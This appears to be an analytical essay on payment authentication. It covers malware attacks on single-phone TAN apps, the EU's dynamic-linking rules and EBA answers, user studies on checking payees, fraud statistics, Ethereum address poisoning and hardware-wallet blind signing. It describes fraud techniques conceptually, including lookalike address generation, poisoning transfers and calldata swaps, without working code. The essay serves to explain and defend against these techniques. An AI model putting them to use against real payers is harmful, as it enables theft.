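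The case study showed that such a code is possible. It did not test whether people can use it, and Kiljan and colleagues leave such experiments to later research. The effort required of customers is therefore known only from the design. They need a device with keys for letters as well as digits, on which they enter a full IBAN. They then copy 16 characters, whereas a Cronto user copies six digits. A code made only of digits would need 25. In an experiment by other researchers, people found short words easiest to copy, but this message would need nine. In return, the customer enters the payment once and does not have to check it against a second screen. A phone could also scan the message as a square barcode, so the customer would not have to copy it.

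The scheme does not work when a web shop supplies the payment details, because the customer does not enter them. It also would not protect a tenant who copies a stranger's account number from a forged email, or customers who think they are taking part in a training exercise, because they enter the thief's details on the trusted device themselves. If the thief is someone the customer intends to pay, malware can display a false notice that the payment has failed, so that the customer pays again. Kiljan and colleagues suggest that banks watch for repeated payments to the same account.

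### Banking and confirming on one phone

Customers found a second device inconvenient, and in 2015 German banks including HypoVereinsbank, DKB and the savings banks were introducing procedures that needed only a phone. The customer enters a transfer in the banking app. A second app on the same phone receives the transfer details and a TAN, and passes the TAN to the banking app.

In *AppTAN (In)Security*, the security researchers Haupert and Müller attacked pushTAN, the savings banks' version. In their demonstration, a customer orders a transfer of €0.10 to the tax office. The pushTAN app displays that recipient and amount, the customer approves the payment, and the banking app reports success. Only the account statement shows that €13.37 has gone to Vincent Haupert.

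Here the bank had sent the true details to an app whose only purpose was to show them. But malware with system rights can change what either app displays, so there was no trusted path from the app to the customer. Haupert and Müller conclude that better programming cannot solve this, because the problem is using one device for both steps.

PhotoTAN protects transfers better when the customer uses two devices. If the customer enters a transfer on a laptop and scans the picture on its screen with a phone, an attacker has to control both devices, and Haupert regards this as sound in principle. FAU's *PhotoTAN-Banking nicht sicher* (2016) explains that a phone cannot photograph its own screen, so when the customer uses only a phone, the banking app contacts the photoTAN app directly. An attacker then needs to infect only that phone. The researchers altered transfers in this way with the apps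 of Deutsche Bank, Commerzbank and Norisbank. They also copied the photoTAN app to another phone, where it produced the same TANs as the original.

Haupert says in FAU (2017) that the banks mostly dismissed the attacks as "an academic laboratory experiment". The savings banks maintain that one device is enough. On their common website, Sparkasse, they tell customers that passwords and cryptographic keys make pushTAN secure, and that the testing organisation TÜV Saarland has examined the app. Reiner SCT's *pushTAN* makes the stronger claim that the method is as secure as chipTAN, because registration divides the phone into two separate "logical channels". That separation depends on the phone's operating system, which the malware in these attacks had taken over.

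The banks were right that the 2015 attack took effort. It required several weeks of analysis and malicious code running on the victim's phone. Haupert and Müller, in *On App-based Matrix Code Authentication in Online Banking*, knew of no public case of loss, though they thought this was partly because few people used such apps yet. They accepted that a bank may trade some security for convenience, but objected to banks advertising the result as equally secure. A TAN is meant to protect people whose computer is already infected, so a procedure that works only on a phone free of malware defeats that purpose.

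By 2017 such attacks took less effort. Many banks had added Promon SHIELD, protective software that blocks transactions on a compromised phone. Haupert and his colleague Nicolas Schneider wrote a program that automatically disabled it in 31 financial apps, regardless of the phone or app version. They tested the program only on Android and only in simulated attacks.

The savings banks made customers responsible for the security of the phone that serves as the trusted display. Sparkasse's *Sorgfaltspflichten pushTAN* (2013), a set of contract terms, forbids customers to remove the manufacturer's restrictions on the phone and allows them to install apps only from safe sources. These terms rule out some risks, but not the case Haupert and Müller assumed, in which malware exploits a flaw in an unmodified phone without the owner noticing.

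A customer can restore the independence by entering payments on a laptop and using the phone only to confirm them. This fails if the bank puts both functions into one app, as N26 did. The customer then has to log in on the phone to confirm, and malware there can capture the login as well. Haupert recommends a separate photoTAN reader that scans the picture from the phone's screen. The reader is small enough to carry, and malware has very little to attack because the device has no other functions or interfaces.

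Some savings banks have nevertheless encouraged customers to replace the separate device with an approval app. Sparkasse Heilbronn's *Change from chipTAN to pushTAN* guides customers through the switch, and Kasseler Sparkasse's *S-pushTAN* (2026) presents the approval app as a companion to the banking app, online banking or finance software.

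## What the EU rule on dynamic linking requires

The EU's second payment services directive (PSD2) requires banks to tie a customer's approval of an online payment to the amount and the payee, a rule known as dynamic linking. *Article 97 Authentication* requires banks and other payment companies to use strong customer authentication when a customer accesses their payment account online, starts an electronic payment, or does anything else remotely that carries a risk of fraud. Strong customer authentication means checking at least two of three kinds of evidence: something the customer knows, such as a PIN, something they have, such as a phone, and something they are, such as a fingerprint.

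That alone would only establish the user's identity. Article 97(2) therefore adds that, for remote payments, the authentication must include "elements which dynamically link the transaction to a specific amount and a specific payee". The directive doesn't explain how. The details are in Article 5 of the European Commission's *Commission Delegated Regulation (EU) 2018/389* (2018), which has applied since 14 September 2019.

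### Article 5, clause by clause

Each clause of Article 5 corresponds mainly to one of Weng's four conditions for an approval.

| Clause | What the bank must ensure | Condition |
|---|---|---|
| 5(1)(a) | The payer is aware of the amount and the payee | All consequential facts shown |
| 5(1)(b) | The authentication code is specific to the amount and payee the payer agreed to | Binding |
| 5(1)(c) | The code the bank accepts corresponds to the original amount and payee | Binding |
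| 5(1)(d) | Any change to the amount or payee invalidates the code | Binding |
| 5(2)(a) | The amount and payee stay confidential, authentic and intact throughout the authentication | Truthful rendering |
| 5(2)(b) | The information displayed to the payer stays confidential, authentic and intact throughout the authentication | Trusted path |

The three clauses on binding overlap but apply at different moments. Clause (b) covers how the code is generated, clause (c) covers the bank's check when the code arrives, and clause (d) covers changes in between. Together they rule out the ordinary one-time code, which malware could use for any payment order.

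Clause (a) lists only the two facts that matter most for a single bank transfer, and these are not always enough. If malware turns the tenant's payment into a monthly order, the bank must apply strong authentication when the series is set up, but Article 5 does not require it to display the word "monthly".

The law covers the trusted path least. Clause 5(2)(b) requires measures that "ensure" the integrity of what the payer sees, which, read literally, would rule out any screen that malware can alter. But when a customer approves payments on a multi-purpose device such as a phone, Article 9 of the same regulation requires the bank only to "mitigate" the risk that an attacker controls it. The bank must use separated secure execution environments, check that nobody has altered the software or the device, and limit the damage if somebody has. The law therefore allows customers to bank and confirm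 payments on the same phone. Haupert and his colleagues had already defeated protective software of this general kind before the regulation applied.

Article 5 also covers only the information that reaches the payer, not the payer's answer. Article 4 requires the bank to protect the session against manipulation by unauthorised parties. This might cover a case like ABN AMRO's USB reader, where the computer could give the command to sign, but no clause requires that only the payer be able to answer.

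### A worked code

The regulation doesn't prescribe a formula. A simple code that would fit its clauses on binding is

code = the last six digits of *H*(*k* | *n* | amount | payee),

where *H* is a hash function whose result we read as a long number, *k* is a secret key that the customer's device shares with the bank, and *n* is a fresh number that the bank uses only once. Each field needs a fixed length. Otherwise an amount of 950 followed by an account number starting with 1 would look the same as an amount of 9501 followed by the rest of that number.

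The codes in this table are invented, but they show how the formula behaves.

| Order | Amount in cents | Payee's account | Fresh number | Code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The rent the tenant approves | 95000 | Landlord's, ending 3000 | 58213 | 683222 |
| The order malware submits | 95000 | Stranger's, ending 8890 | 58213 | 107459 |
| Next month's rent | 95000 | Landlord's, ending 3000 | 58214 | 940336 |

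The tenant sees the landlord's account and €950 on a trusted device, approves, and gets the code 683222. Malware on the laptop then replaces the account number and sends the same code. The bank computes the code for the order it received, gets 107459, and rejects the payment because the codes don't match. The malware cannot work out 107459 because it doesn't have the key.

In the third row, only the fresh number has changed, so last month's code no longer works even though the rent is the same. Article 4 separately requires the bank to accept each code only once.

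The malware can still guess. A six-digit code has a million possible values, and the European Commission's regulation allows at most five consecutive failed attempts before the bank blocks further ones. The chance of success is

5 / 1,000,000 = 1 in 200,000.

Trying the old code counts as one of the five guesses and is no more likely to work than any other. The risk to any one customer is small, but a gang that made five guesses on each of 200,000 infected computers could expect about one success.

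The limit applies "within a given period of time", and the block may be temporary. If a bank lifted the block every day, malware that guessed five times a day for a year would make 1,825 attempts and have about a 1 in 550 chance of guessing correctly. The regulation doesn't set the length of the block, but the bank must take the risk into account when choosing it, and must warn the customer before making a block permanent. Adding two digits to the code would make each of these chances a hundred times smaller.

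The attacker doesn't need to guess at all if the tenant approves the stranger's account on the device.

### What the European Banking Authority has answered

The European Banking Authority (EBA), the EU agency that drafted these technical standards, publishes answers to questions about them. One questioner asked whether a code computed from only the digits of an IBAN would be enough, because some hardware tokens have only number keys and customers can't enter the letters. The EBA answered in *Definition of payee for dynamic linking* that a bank may include a meaningful part of the IBAN in the code, "or none at all", provided it still meets every requirement of Article 5(1).

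A code can meet the rule even if it contains no information about the payment. The bank can store the tenant's order, generate a random code, and record that the code is valid only for that order. If anyone changes the payee, the bank cancels the code, so it cannot be used to pay anyone but the landlord. Here the bank's records link the code to the payment, whereas the worked example relied on a calculation by the customer's device.

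Using only part of the account number is riskier. Suppose a token computes the code from the amount and the last four digits of the account number, with no other check. About one account in 10,000 shares the landlord's last four digits. Anyone can look for such an account, and a thief who gets hold of one can change the payee without changing the code. That would violate clause (d), so the bank would need a further safeguard. Two full account numbers can also produce the same six-digit code by chance, about once in a million, but a thief can't find such a match in advance without knowing the key.

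The rule is harder to apply to batch payments, where a business may pay thousands of suppliers in one order. The Central Bank of Malta asked whether the authentication code must depend on every IBAN in the batch. The EBA's *Dynamic Linking for batch payments* says that it must, so changing, adding or deleting a single IBAN must invalidate the code. A hash function makes this manageable, because its digest is the same length however many IBANs the batch contains.

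A short display cannot list ten thousand payees, however. When asked whether the payer must be made aware of each one, the EBA answered in *Dynamic linking for batch transactions* that the payer "should be able to check the payees list" if they wish to. The duty to bind the approval is therefore stricter than the duty to display what it covers.

RedTeam Pentesting's attack on chipTAN, which swapped the payees in a collective transfer, used this gap. A code that depended on every IBAN would not have prevented the attack, because the IBANs would have been the thief's. The payer could have discovered the swap by checking the list, but only on a screen the malware did not control. If the list is available only on the infected laptop, the malware can show the original suppliers instead. Clause 5(2)(b) should rule that out, since the list is also information displayed to the payer, but the EBA's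 answer doesn't address where the payer reads it.

Sometimes nobody knows the final amount when the customer approves a payment. The European Banking Federation gave the example of groceries ordered online. The shop weighs the fruit and replaces missing items at 4 a.m., when the customer is asleep and can't authenticate again. The Federation argued that the final sum should be allowed to rise within the customer's reasonable expectations, because the customer has already authenticated a legitimate purchase and PSD2 gives them a right to a refund if the charge is unexpectedly high.

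The EBA accepted only half of this. Under the EBA's *Dynamic linking*, if the exact amount of a card payment is known in advance, the final amount must be the same as the one approved. If it isn't known, a lower or equal final amount can go through on the original code, but for a higher one the bank must authenticate the customer again or decline the payment. In that case, a customer who approved €100 can be charged €96 without authenticating again, but not €104.

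In such cases the approved amount is a ceiling. This still protects the customer, because the code doesn't permit a payment larger than the amount they saw. The Federation's alternative would have relied on the customer noticing a higher charge and getting a refund after the money had left. The Federation's complaint about inconvenience has some force, but a shop can ask the customer to approve a somewhat higher maximum at the start. The Federation also worried that this would freeze customers' money for days. The EBA's answer reduces that problem by applying the same ceiling when the bank doesn't block any funds.

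In other cases, the phone does not yet have the amount or the payee when the customer authenticates. An industry group working on mobile transfers described such systems and asked where the bank must compute the code. The EBA's *Clarification on where the creation of the authentication code with dynamic linking* allows the bank to compute it away from the payer's device, at any stage before the payer's final authorisation. The payer must still learn the amount and payee, and the bank must protect both details and their display throughout.

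Dynamic linking is weaker than "what you see is what you sign" in one respect, because the law doesn't require the customer's device to sign the payment details or even to receive them in a form it can check. A bank can do all the computation on its own server, as long as the customer sees the true details before giving final approval. This design can stop malware on a laptop if the details appear on a separate screen. In a later dispute, though, the evidence of what the customer approved is largely the bank's own records.

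### Secure Payment Confirmation

Secure Payment Confirmation, a web specification from the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), has the customer's device sign the payment details. It extends passkeys, which normally sign only a random challenge and some technical data about the website.

Suppose the tenant has registered a passkey with their bank and then buys a €60 lamp online. At the checkout, the shop's page passes the browser a fresh challenge from the bank, along with the amount, the currency and the shop's name or web address. The browser displays the payment details in its own dialog, beside the name of the card. When the tenant confirms with a fingerprint or a PIN, the browser writes the challenge and the payment details into a record and computes a digest of that record. The authenticator signs the digest along with some data of its own. The bank then verifies the signature and checks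 that the amount and payee in the record match the payment it is about to execute.

If the shop changes €60 to €600 after the tenant confirms, the record no longer matches. If it changes the amount beforehand, the dialog shows €600. A hacked shop page can't make the dialog show a different sum from the record, because the browser fills in both from the same values. The challenge serves as the fresh number from the worked example. The signature replaces the six digits, which makes guessing impractical.

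Secure Payment Confirmation uses the browser as its trusted display, but man-in-the-browser malware takes over the browser. The authenticator receives a digest, which doesn't reveal whether the payment is €60 to a lamp shop or €600 to a thief. Malware with enough control over the browser could display the first payment and submit the second for signing, as the mail program did with Balfanz and Felten's smart card. Secure Payment Confirmation therefore protects the customer from a dishonest web page, but not from a compromised host. It also identifies the payee by a shop's name or web address, which suits card purchases better than a transfer to a landlord's account number.

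### Payments that need no code

Dynamic linking applies only when the bank has to authenticate the payment, and the European Commission's regulation exempts several kinds of payment from authentication. A bank may skip it for a remote payment of up to €30 if the earlier ones since the last authentication total no more than €100 or number no more than five. It may also skip it for transfers between a customer's own accounts at the same bank, and for later payments in a series with the same amount and payee. Companies can use dedicated payment systems without authentication if the authorities consider those systems at least as secure.

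A bank can exempt payments of up to €500 that it judges to be low-risk. This is the highest limit of any exemption that covers ordinary customers' payments to new payees. To use it, the bank must keep fraud below a set share of the value of its payments.

| Payment up to | Maximum fraud rate, cards | Maximum fraud rate, transfers |
|---|---|---|
| €100 | 0.13% | 0.015% |
| €250 | 0.06% | 0.01% |
| €500 | 0.01% | 0.005% |

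To exempt transfers of up to €500, a bank must thus keep fraud to no more than €5 in every €100,000 transferred. It must also check each payment for abnormal spending, signs of malware and other warnings. The €950 rent is too large for this exemption. But malware could attempt a €450 transfer to a stranger, and if the bank's checks found nothing unusual, the transfer would not appear on a trusted display.

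A customer can also put the landlord on a list of trusted beneficiaries. Payments to anyone on the list need no code, whatever the amount. The bank must authenticate the customer when they change the list, but Article 5 applies only to authentication under Article 97(2), which concerns payments, and changing the list is not a payment. On the wording alone, the code for adding a payee therefore doesn't have to be specific to that payee. Malware could ask the tenant to approve adding the landlord, add the stranger instead, and later pay the stranger without any approval. A careful bank will still display the name and account being added, and its monitoring may catch the payment, but the rule doesn't explicitly require dynamic linking for this approval, which can cover many transfers.

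### The Payment Services Regulation

The EU is replacing most of PSD2 with a Payment Services Regulation, which will apply in every member state without national legislation. The European Commission's *Explanatory Memorandum to COM(2023)367* (2023), which accompanied the proposal, cites an evaluation that found strong authentication harder to introduce than expected but already effective in reducing fraud. That finding covers strong authentication as a whole, so it doesn't show how much of the reduction came from dynamic linking.

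The regulation is not yet law. *Two EU sites, two clocks* (Berryman, 2026) reported that the Council, which represents the member states' governments, adopted its position on 29 October 2026 by 27 votes to 0. Parliament still has to hold a second reading, though the chair of its economic committee said in May that she would recommend accepting the text unamended. Legal 500's *EU PSD3/PSR* (2026) still listed Parliament's adoption as outstanding on 19 November.

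Reports differ on when the new rules would apply. Mondaq's *PSD3 and PSR final compromise texts published* gives 21 months after entry into force for most of them and 27 for the checks on payees' names. *Ue*, from the news agency Il Sole 24 Ore Radiocor, gives 18 to 21 months after publication. If the new regulation is published in January 2027, its dynamic linking rules would apply from late 2028 on Mondaq's timetable.

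The compromise text that the Council of the EU (2026) published in April keeps the central sentence almost unchanged. Remote payment orders still need authentication that links them to a specific amount and a specific payee. The text also covers payments where a customer holds their own device near a shop's terminal and must use that device's internet connection to authenticate. For these, a bank can use dynamic linking or other harmonised measures "of identical effect".

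Some payments would remain outside the rule, and others would move outside it. Charges that a merchant initiates without the customer's involvement need no strong authentication, although the customer must authenticate when setting up the mandate remotely with the bank's involvement. A new article treats recurring bank transfers requested by the payee similarly. For example, if a tenant agrees that the landlord may collect rent plus heating costs and authenticates that agreement once, later transfers can vary in amount without another approval. The agreement has to state when the amounts can vary, but the tenant will not see each sum before the bank pays it.

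The text also allows both pieces of evidence to be biometric, such as a fingerprint and a face scan, if the bank can show that they are independent. Two biometric checks establish only who is approving, so this strengthens neither the display nor the binding. More usefully for people who don't want to bank and confirm on one phone, a bank could not make authentication depend on owning a smartphone unless the customer had agreed to a service available only through mobile apps. It would have to offer at least one suitable method free of charge, but its duty to support customers would not include supplying devices. National authorities would have to be able to fine companies that breach the authentication rules, with a maximum fine of at least 10% of annual turnover.

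The Council of the EU's text leaves most of the detail now in Article 5 to new technical standards, which the EBA must draft within a year after the regulation enters into force. Those standards will determine how a bank must protect the display, what it may exempt, and whether measures that only "mitigate" the risk of a compromised phone are still enough.

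## What customers notice on a truthful screen

Even if the bank and the device work perfectly and a trusted display shows the stranger's account number, the tenant still has to notice it. To find out whether people do, Haupert and Gabert (2019), in *Where to Look for What You See Is What You Sign?*, asked 100 online banking customers to pay two invoices by credit transfer. Participants confirmed the attacked payment by the same method they used with their own bank, so unfamiliar equipment cannot explain the results.

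During the second transfer, Haupert and Gabert secretly replaced the payee's account number, as malware in the browser would. Malware like Silentbanker puts the original number back on the bank's confirmation page, which asks for the one-time code, but the researchers left the fraudulent number there. This gave the customer another chance to spot the wrong number, but it also made the web page match the device, as the table shows.

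| What the customer compares | Malware restores the original number on the page | Malware leaves the fraudulent number on the page |
|---|---|---|
| Web page with invoice | Same | Different |
| Device with web page | Different | Same |
| Device with invoice | Different | Different |

A customer who compares the device's screen with the invoice will detect either attack. Many participants instead compared it with the fraudulent details on the web page, so they could check every digit correctly and still approve the theft. A majority did not verify their transactions at all.

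Participants were less likely to fall for the attack if they had a technical background or had experience with several confirmation methods or with certain ones. Practice may have helped, but the researchers didn't assign anyone to these groups, and people who try several methods may be more careful to begin with. People may also check an invoice in an experiment less carefully than their own bills, so the results could overstate how often customers would fall for the attack at home.

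In his doctoral thesis, *Sicherheit mobiler Bankgeschäfte zwischen Innovation und Regulierung*, Haupert (2019) attributes both the faulty checks and the missing ones to customers often not knowing which steps matter for security. He also blames the banks for giving them misleading information. In April 2019, for example, Haupert and Gabert found that the confirmation page of the savings bank in Nuremberg showed the full transaction details to customers who received codes by text message or app, but none to customers with chipTAN.

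A customer who always sees the payment details next to the field for the code will naturally compare the phone with the page. Banks could remove the details from the page, but malware could put them back. An instruction on the trusted device, such as "Compare this number with your invoice", would probably help more.

### Text messages, card readers and QR codes

Two years earlier, Rötting, Schmuntzsch and Paulisch had run experiments with text-message codes and chipTAN at the Technical University of Berlin. They report in *Betrugsschutz beim Online-Banking* (2017) that on average 56% of participants did not compare the IBAN. A majority also skipped verification in Haupert and Gabert's study. In the part of the Berlin research on phishing and trojans, 28% used the code without checking either the amount or the IBAN. The two figures are compatible, because many people may check the amount but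 not the IBAN. They would miss malware that changes only the payee.

The Berlin researchers emphasized attention more than knowledge. Participants rated text messages significantly better than chipTAN on four of six usability measures, including controllability (1.74 against 2.70, where lower is better). According to the slides (TU Berlin, 2017), the chipTAN device often failed to read the transaction data from the screen, and getting it to work took all of the participants' attention. Once it worked, they had "tunnel vision" and finished the transaction quickly.

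Both explanations can be true. A customer may not know to check the displayed details against the invoice, or may know but be too relieved that the flicker code has finally worked to do so. The second problem is awkward for designers because the separate reader is the safer device, but using it can leave the customer impatient just before the details appear.

Customers also seem more likely to notice fraud when they type the payment details than when they scan them. *Scanned and Scammed* reports three experiments with 1,876 participants, in which only 13% recognised fraudulent payment requests in QR codes, compared with 46% when people entered the details by hand. People have to look at an account number to type it, but not to scan it. This gives some support to the proposal by Kiljan and colleagues to have customers enter the payment on the trusted device. But typing isn't enough when the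 request itself is fraudulent, since more than half of the people who typed the details still missed the fraud.

### Long identifiers and look-alike addresses

An account number is hard to check because it has no meaning. The tenant can recognise the landlord's name at a glance, but they have to compare the 22 characters of a German IBAN a few at a time, looking back and forth between two screens. Almost every transfer is legitimate, so the numbers almost always match, and people save time by checking only the beginning and the end.

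Comparing only the last four digits works surprisingly well for bank accounts. Few accounts share the landlord's, and a thief can't choose a matching number because banks assign the numbers. Opening thousands of accounts to get a match would be expensive.

Cryptocurrency has no such obstacle. On Ethereum, a public network for cryptocurrency and small programs, an address consists of 40 hexadecimal characters, each of which can take 16 values (the digits 0 to 9 and the letters a to f). Anyone can generate addresses on their own computer, without asking anybody, and keep the ones that look right. Suppose a user checks only the first four and last four characters. A random address matches all eight with a probability of 1 in 16<sup>8</sup>, so an attacker needs on average

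16<sup>8</sup> = 4,294,967,296, or about 4.3 billion, tries.

A computer that tests a million addresses a second would take about 72 minutes to find one that matches the first four and last four characters of a given address. If the user checked five characters at each end, the search would take 256 times as long, or almost 13 days. Matching all 40 characters is infeasible, so the full address is a good identifier, but users who habitually check only eight characters can mistake a lookalike for it.

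The attacker doesn't have to choose the victim first. *There Will Be Spam* (2026) describes how attackers generate addresses, then monitor the network for transactions that involve similar ones. A million stored addresses and a million addresses in use make a trillion possible pairs, and about 230 of those would match in those eight characters by chance.

An attack called address poisoning relies on the way wallets shorten addresses on the screen. Say a company regularly pays a supplier on Ethereum. The attacker sends the company a transaction from an address that begins and ends like the supplier's. Both addresses now appear in the company's transaction history, and an employee may copy the attacker's address the next time the company pays the supplier.

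According to *There Will Be Spam*, attackers typically put the entry there in one of three ways:

- A zero-value transfer moves nothing, but still creates an entry in the history, at very little cost.
- A dust-value transfer moves a tiny sum, which makes the entry look more legitimate.
- A fake-token transfer uses an imitation of a real digital currency.

None of this requires malware, and a trusted display doesn't stop it. If the employee confirms the payment on a device that no attacker can tamper with, the device accurately displays the attacker's address. The employee compares the first and last characters of that address with the entry in the history, and they match. As with the web page in Haupert and Gabert's experiment, the attacker has supplied the reference that the employee checks against.

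A single mistake can be very expensive. *The Anatomy of Address Poisoning on Ethereum* (2026) cites a 2023 post by the cryptocurrency exchange Binance about an attempted $20 million scam. That figure is for one attempt and does not measure total losses.

The employee can make the check stronger with little extra effort by also comparing four characters picked at random from the middle. An attacker who has matched only the ends then gets past the check about once in 65,000 cases. The employee still needs a reference that the attacker could not write to, such as an address book the company filled in when it first dealt with the supplier.

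### When the payer means to pay

In the cases so far, the display showed a wrong account number that the payer could in principle have caught. In other frauds, the display accurately shows who will be paid and how much, and the payer reads it and approves the payment because a fraudster has deceived them with a false story.

UK Finance, the trade association of British banks, calls this authorised push payment fraud and divides it into two groups. In "malicious redirection", the payer means to pay someone legitimate but sends the money elsewhere. UK Finance gives the example of a house buyer who wants to send a deposit to a solicitor but receives new account details from a criminal. In "malicious payee" fraud, the money reaches the person or company the payer intended, who then disappears with it, as in investment scams and sales by fake online sellers.

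In UK Finance's *Annual Fraud Report 2026* (2026), malicious payee fraud accounts for £437 million of the £576.4 million that British customers lost to authorised fraud in 2025. Losses to malicious payee fraud rose by 35% in a year, although some date from earlier years, because victims of investment or romance scams may take years to realise what has happened. Redirection fraud has fallen from over half of authorised losses in 2020 to just under a quarter.

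The *2025 Report on Payment Fraud*, by the European Banking Authority and the European Central Bank, gives the latest figures for the European Economic Area. Fraudulent credit transfers came to €2.5 billion in 2024, 24% more than in 2023. Fraudsters had manipulated the payer in 74% of these transfers by value, up from 65%.

The table compares frauds that manipulate the payer with frauds in which somebody else issued or changed the payment order. The British figures for the first half of 2026 come from The Paypers' *UK Finance*.

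| Region and period | Payer manipulated | Order issued or changed by someone else |
|---|---|---|
| EEA credit transfers, second half of 2024 | 76% of fraud by value | 23% issued by the fraudster, 1% changed |
| UK, 2025 | £576.4 million | £104.4 million (remote banking) |
| UK, first half of 2026 | £316 million | £56.2 million (remote banking) |

British banks recorded another £599 million of unauthorised fraud in 2025, nearly all of it on cards. The table leaves this out because stolen card numbers are a different problem from bank transfer fraud.

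The 1% is the category closest to the man-in-the-browser attack, and amounts to about €10 million in half a year across about 30 countries. Such a low figure is consistent with dynamic linking working, since malware that changes the payee also invalidates the approval, but the data don't prove that this is the reason.

The main difficulty is that the figures begin in 2022 and the rule has applied since September 2019, so we can't compare them with a period before the rule. Altered transfers may already have been a small part of the total before then. Silentbanker, for example, mostly stole passwords, because that was easier.

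Shares can also mislead, because when manipulation grows, the share of every other kind of fraud shrinks even if the amount stays the same. The amount lost to fraud without manipulation of the payer hardly changed between 2023 and 2024. It was about 35% of €2.0 billion in 2023, or €0.7 billion, and 26% of €2.5 billion in 2024, or €0.65 billion.

Comparing authenticated payments with the rest does not help either. The EBA and ECB found higher fraud rates for credit transfers with strong authentication than for those without it. They think this is probably because banks apply it to larger and riskier payments and exempt the safe ones, which is plausible. Their comparison for cards is more convincing. Fraud rates were about seventeen times higher when the recipient was outside the European Economic Area, where the rule may not apply, than for domestic payments. But those countries may differ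 in other ways, and the figure covers strong authentication as a whole, not specifically the link to an amount and a payee. The EBA accepts that the benefit for credit transfers is less clear.

British remote banking losses are also hard to interpret. They fell by 27% in 2025. In their foreword to the UK Finance report, BioCatch and Nasdaq Verafin, which sell fraud detection, write that malware and remote-access fraud have declined as criminals turn to deceiving people. But in the first half of 2026, losses rose by 15% and cases by 38%, according to The Paypers.

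About three quarters of the money that fraudsters take through European credit transfers goes out in payments that dynamic linking could not stop even if every bank implemented it perfectly. Dynamic linking ties the authentication code to the amount and the payee, and in these payments the payer has chosen both. The high share may partly be a sign that dynamic linking works, if criminals are deceiving payers because altering payments has become too difficult.

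### Checking the payee's name

Banks can make redirection easier to notice by letting the payer check a name, which is easier to read than an account number. The tenant enters the landlord's name and IBAN, and before the tenant approves the payment, the tenant's bank asks the bank that holds the account to compare the name with its records. The British service is called Confirmation of Payee. The EU's version, Verification of Payee, became mandatory for most banks in the euro area on 9 October 2025.

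If the name matches, the tenant sees a confirmation. If it nearly matches, as with "Jo Weber" for "Johanna Weber", the tenant sees the name on the account and can decide whether it is the right person. If it doesn't match, the tenant sees a warning that the money may go to someone else. The tenant can go ahead with the transfer in all these cases, and also when the other bank cannot answer.

Checking the payee's name against the bank's records helps even when the tenant has copied a stranger's IBAN from a forged email, because the stranger's bank has a different name on file. An Ethereum address has no bank that could make this check.

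Malware on the laptop can defeat the name check if the result appears only on the laptop's screen. It can submit the stranger's account under the landlord's name and hide the warning, or submit the stranger's real name so that the check succeeds. The tenant would notice either trick if the trusted device displayed the name that the other bank holds for the account, which is much easier to judge than a 22-character account number.

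There is little evidence on how much money these checks save. British losses from redirection fell from more than £210 million in 2020 to about £139 million in 2025, as one would expect if the checks worked. But UK Finance credits general investment in fraud prevention and customer education, and writes only that name checks and warnings "may help" to catch such payments earlier. Criminals may also have moved to investment scams because they pay better. The EU figures end in 2024, before the checks became mandatory, so they cannot show whether mandatory checks reduced losses.

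Name checks do almost nothing against a malicious payee, because the name is correct. UK Finance expects people who believe in an investment to go ahead whatever the warning. A fraudster on the telephone can also prepare the victim for a mismatch, for instance by claiming that the company collects payments through an accountant.

A warning can even make things worse. heise online's *Digital payment transactions* describes a survey for a study by vzbv, the German federation of consumer organisations, in which only 16% of the scam victims recognised the scam after a warning message from their bank. Many consumers took such messages as confirmation that they were doing everything correctly. The 16% figure probably understates how well warnings work, because someone who heeds a warning in time never becomes a victim, but it is still a bad sign if customers treat a fraud warning as a normal step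 in a payment.

### Faithful and understood

A display is faithful if its text matches the order the bank will execute. To understand it, the payer needs to know things that aren't in the order, such as the landlord's real account number and that this is the time to compare it with the one on the screen.

In an investment scam, the screen can correctly show the company's name, the account and the £20,000, but not that the company will vanish next month. The payment order does not contain that information, so no program can derive it from the order. Weng's requirement that a display show all consequential facts covers what the action itself does, but it cannot cover what the recipient intends to do afterwards. Banks can only estimate that from other evidence, such as the recipient's history or a series of increasingly large payments.

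Since October 2024, UK banks have had to reimburse most victims of authorised fraud, even though the victims approved the payments themselves. The Payment Systems Regulator (2026) reports that victims got back 88% of the money the scheme covered in its first 18 months. Banks rejected only 3% of claims for lack of care by the customer. In the European Economic Area, customers bore around 85% of the losses from fraudulent credit transfers in 2024, according to the EBA and ECB.

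## Blind and clear signing on hardware wallets

A cryptocurrency owner has no bank that could question a payment or refund it. Whoever has the private key controls the money, so many owners keep the key in a hardware wallet. The device signs transactions internally and never passes the key to the laptop, much like the smart card in Balfanz and Felten's example. Unlike the card, it has a screen and buttons. As long as the device hasn't been compromised, malware on the laptop can't copy the key, change what the device displays or press its Approve button.

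But the device also has to be able to interpret what it displays. A bank's reader receives an account number and an amount, whereas a hardware wallet often receives a string of bytes meant for a program. If the wallet can't interpret those bytes, its owner has to approve the transaction without seeing it in readable form, which is called blind signing. Ledger's *The Evolution of Clear Signing* (2026) accepts that a secure screen alone cannot prevent this, an admission that carries some weight because Ledger sells such screens.

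### One transfer, byte by byte

Suppose the company that pays a supplier on Ethereum now owes 1,500 USDC, a token worth about one dollar each. A smart contract, which is a program stored on the network, keeps the record of who owns how many USDC. To pay, the company sends this contract a transaction containing calldata, the bytes that tell a smart contract which function to run and with which arguments. Here it is in hexadecimal, split into its three parts:

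```
a9059cbb
0000000000000000000000005aaeb6053f3e94c9b9a09f33669435e7ef1beaed
0000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000059682f00
```

The first part is the function selector, which is the first four bytes (eight hexadecimal characters) of the hash of the text "transfer(address,uint256)". That text consists of the function's name and the types of its two arguments, an address and a whole number.

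The second part is the supplier's address. Every argument here takes up 64 characters and an address has only 40, so 24 zeros fill the rest. The third part is the amount. Hexadecimal 59682f00 is 1,500,000,000 in ordinary notation, and the USDC contract counts in millionths of a token (six decimals), so the company is paying

1,500,000,000 / 10<sup>6</sup> = 1,500 USDC.

The calldata doesn't include the name "USDC" or the token's number of decimals, which is six. The device can identify the token from the contract's address, which is elsewhere in the transaction, but it has to get the name and decimals from another source.

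If malware replaces the selector a9059cbb with 095ea7b3, the transaction calls "approve" instead of "transfer". The supplier's address then receives no money but can withdraw up to 1,500 USDC at any time. The selector also doesn't prove what a function does, because anyone can publish a contract with a function called "transfer" that does something else. The device therefore has to check the contract's address as well.

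### What the device displays when it can't decode a call

Ledger says its devices have always decoded simple transfers of currency and tokens, so the company would probably see the amount and the payee. If the device didn't recognise the USDC contract, however, it might display something like this:

```
Contract   0xa0b86991c6218b36c1d19d4a2e9eb0ce3606eb48
Amount     0 ETH
Data       a9059cbb0000000000000000000000005aaeb605
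           3f3e94c9b9a09f33669435e7ef1beaed00000000...
```

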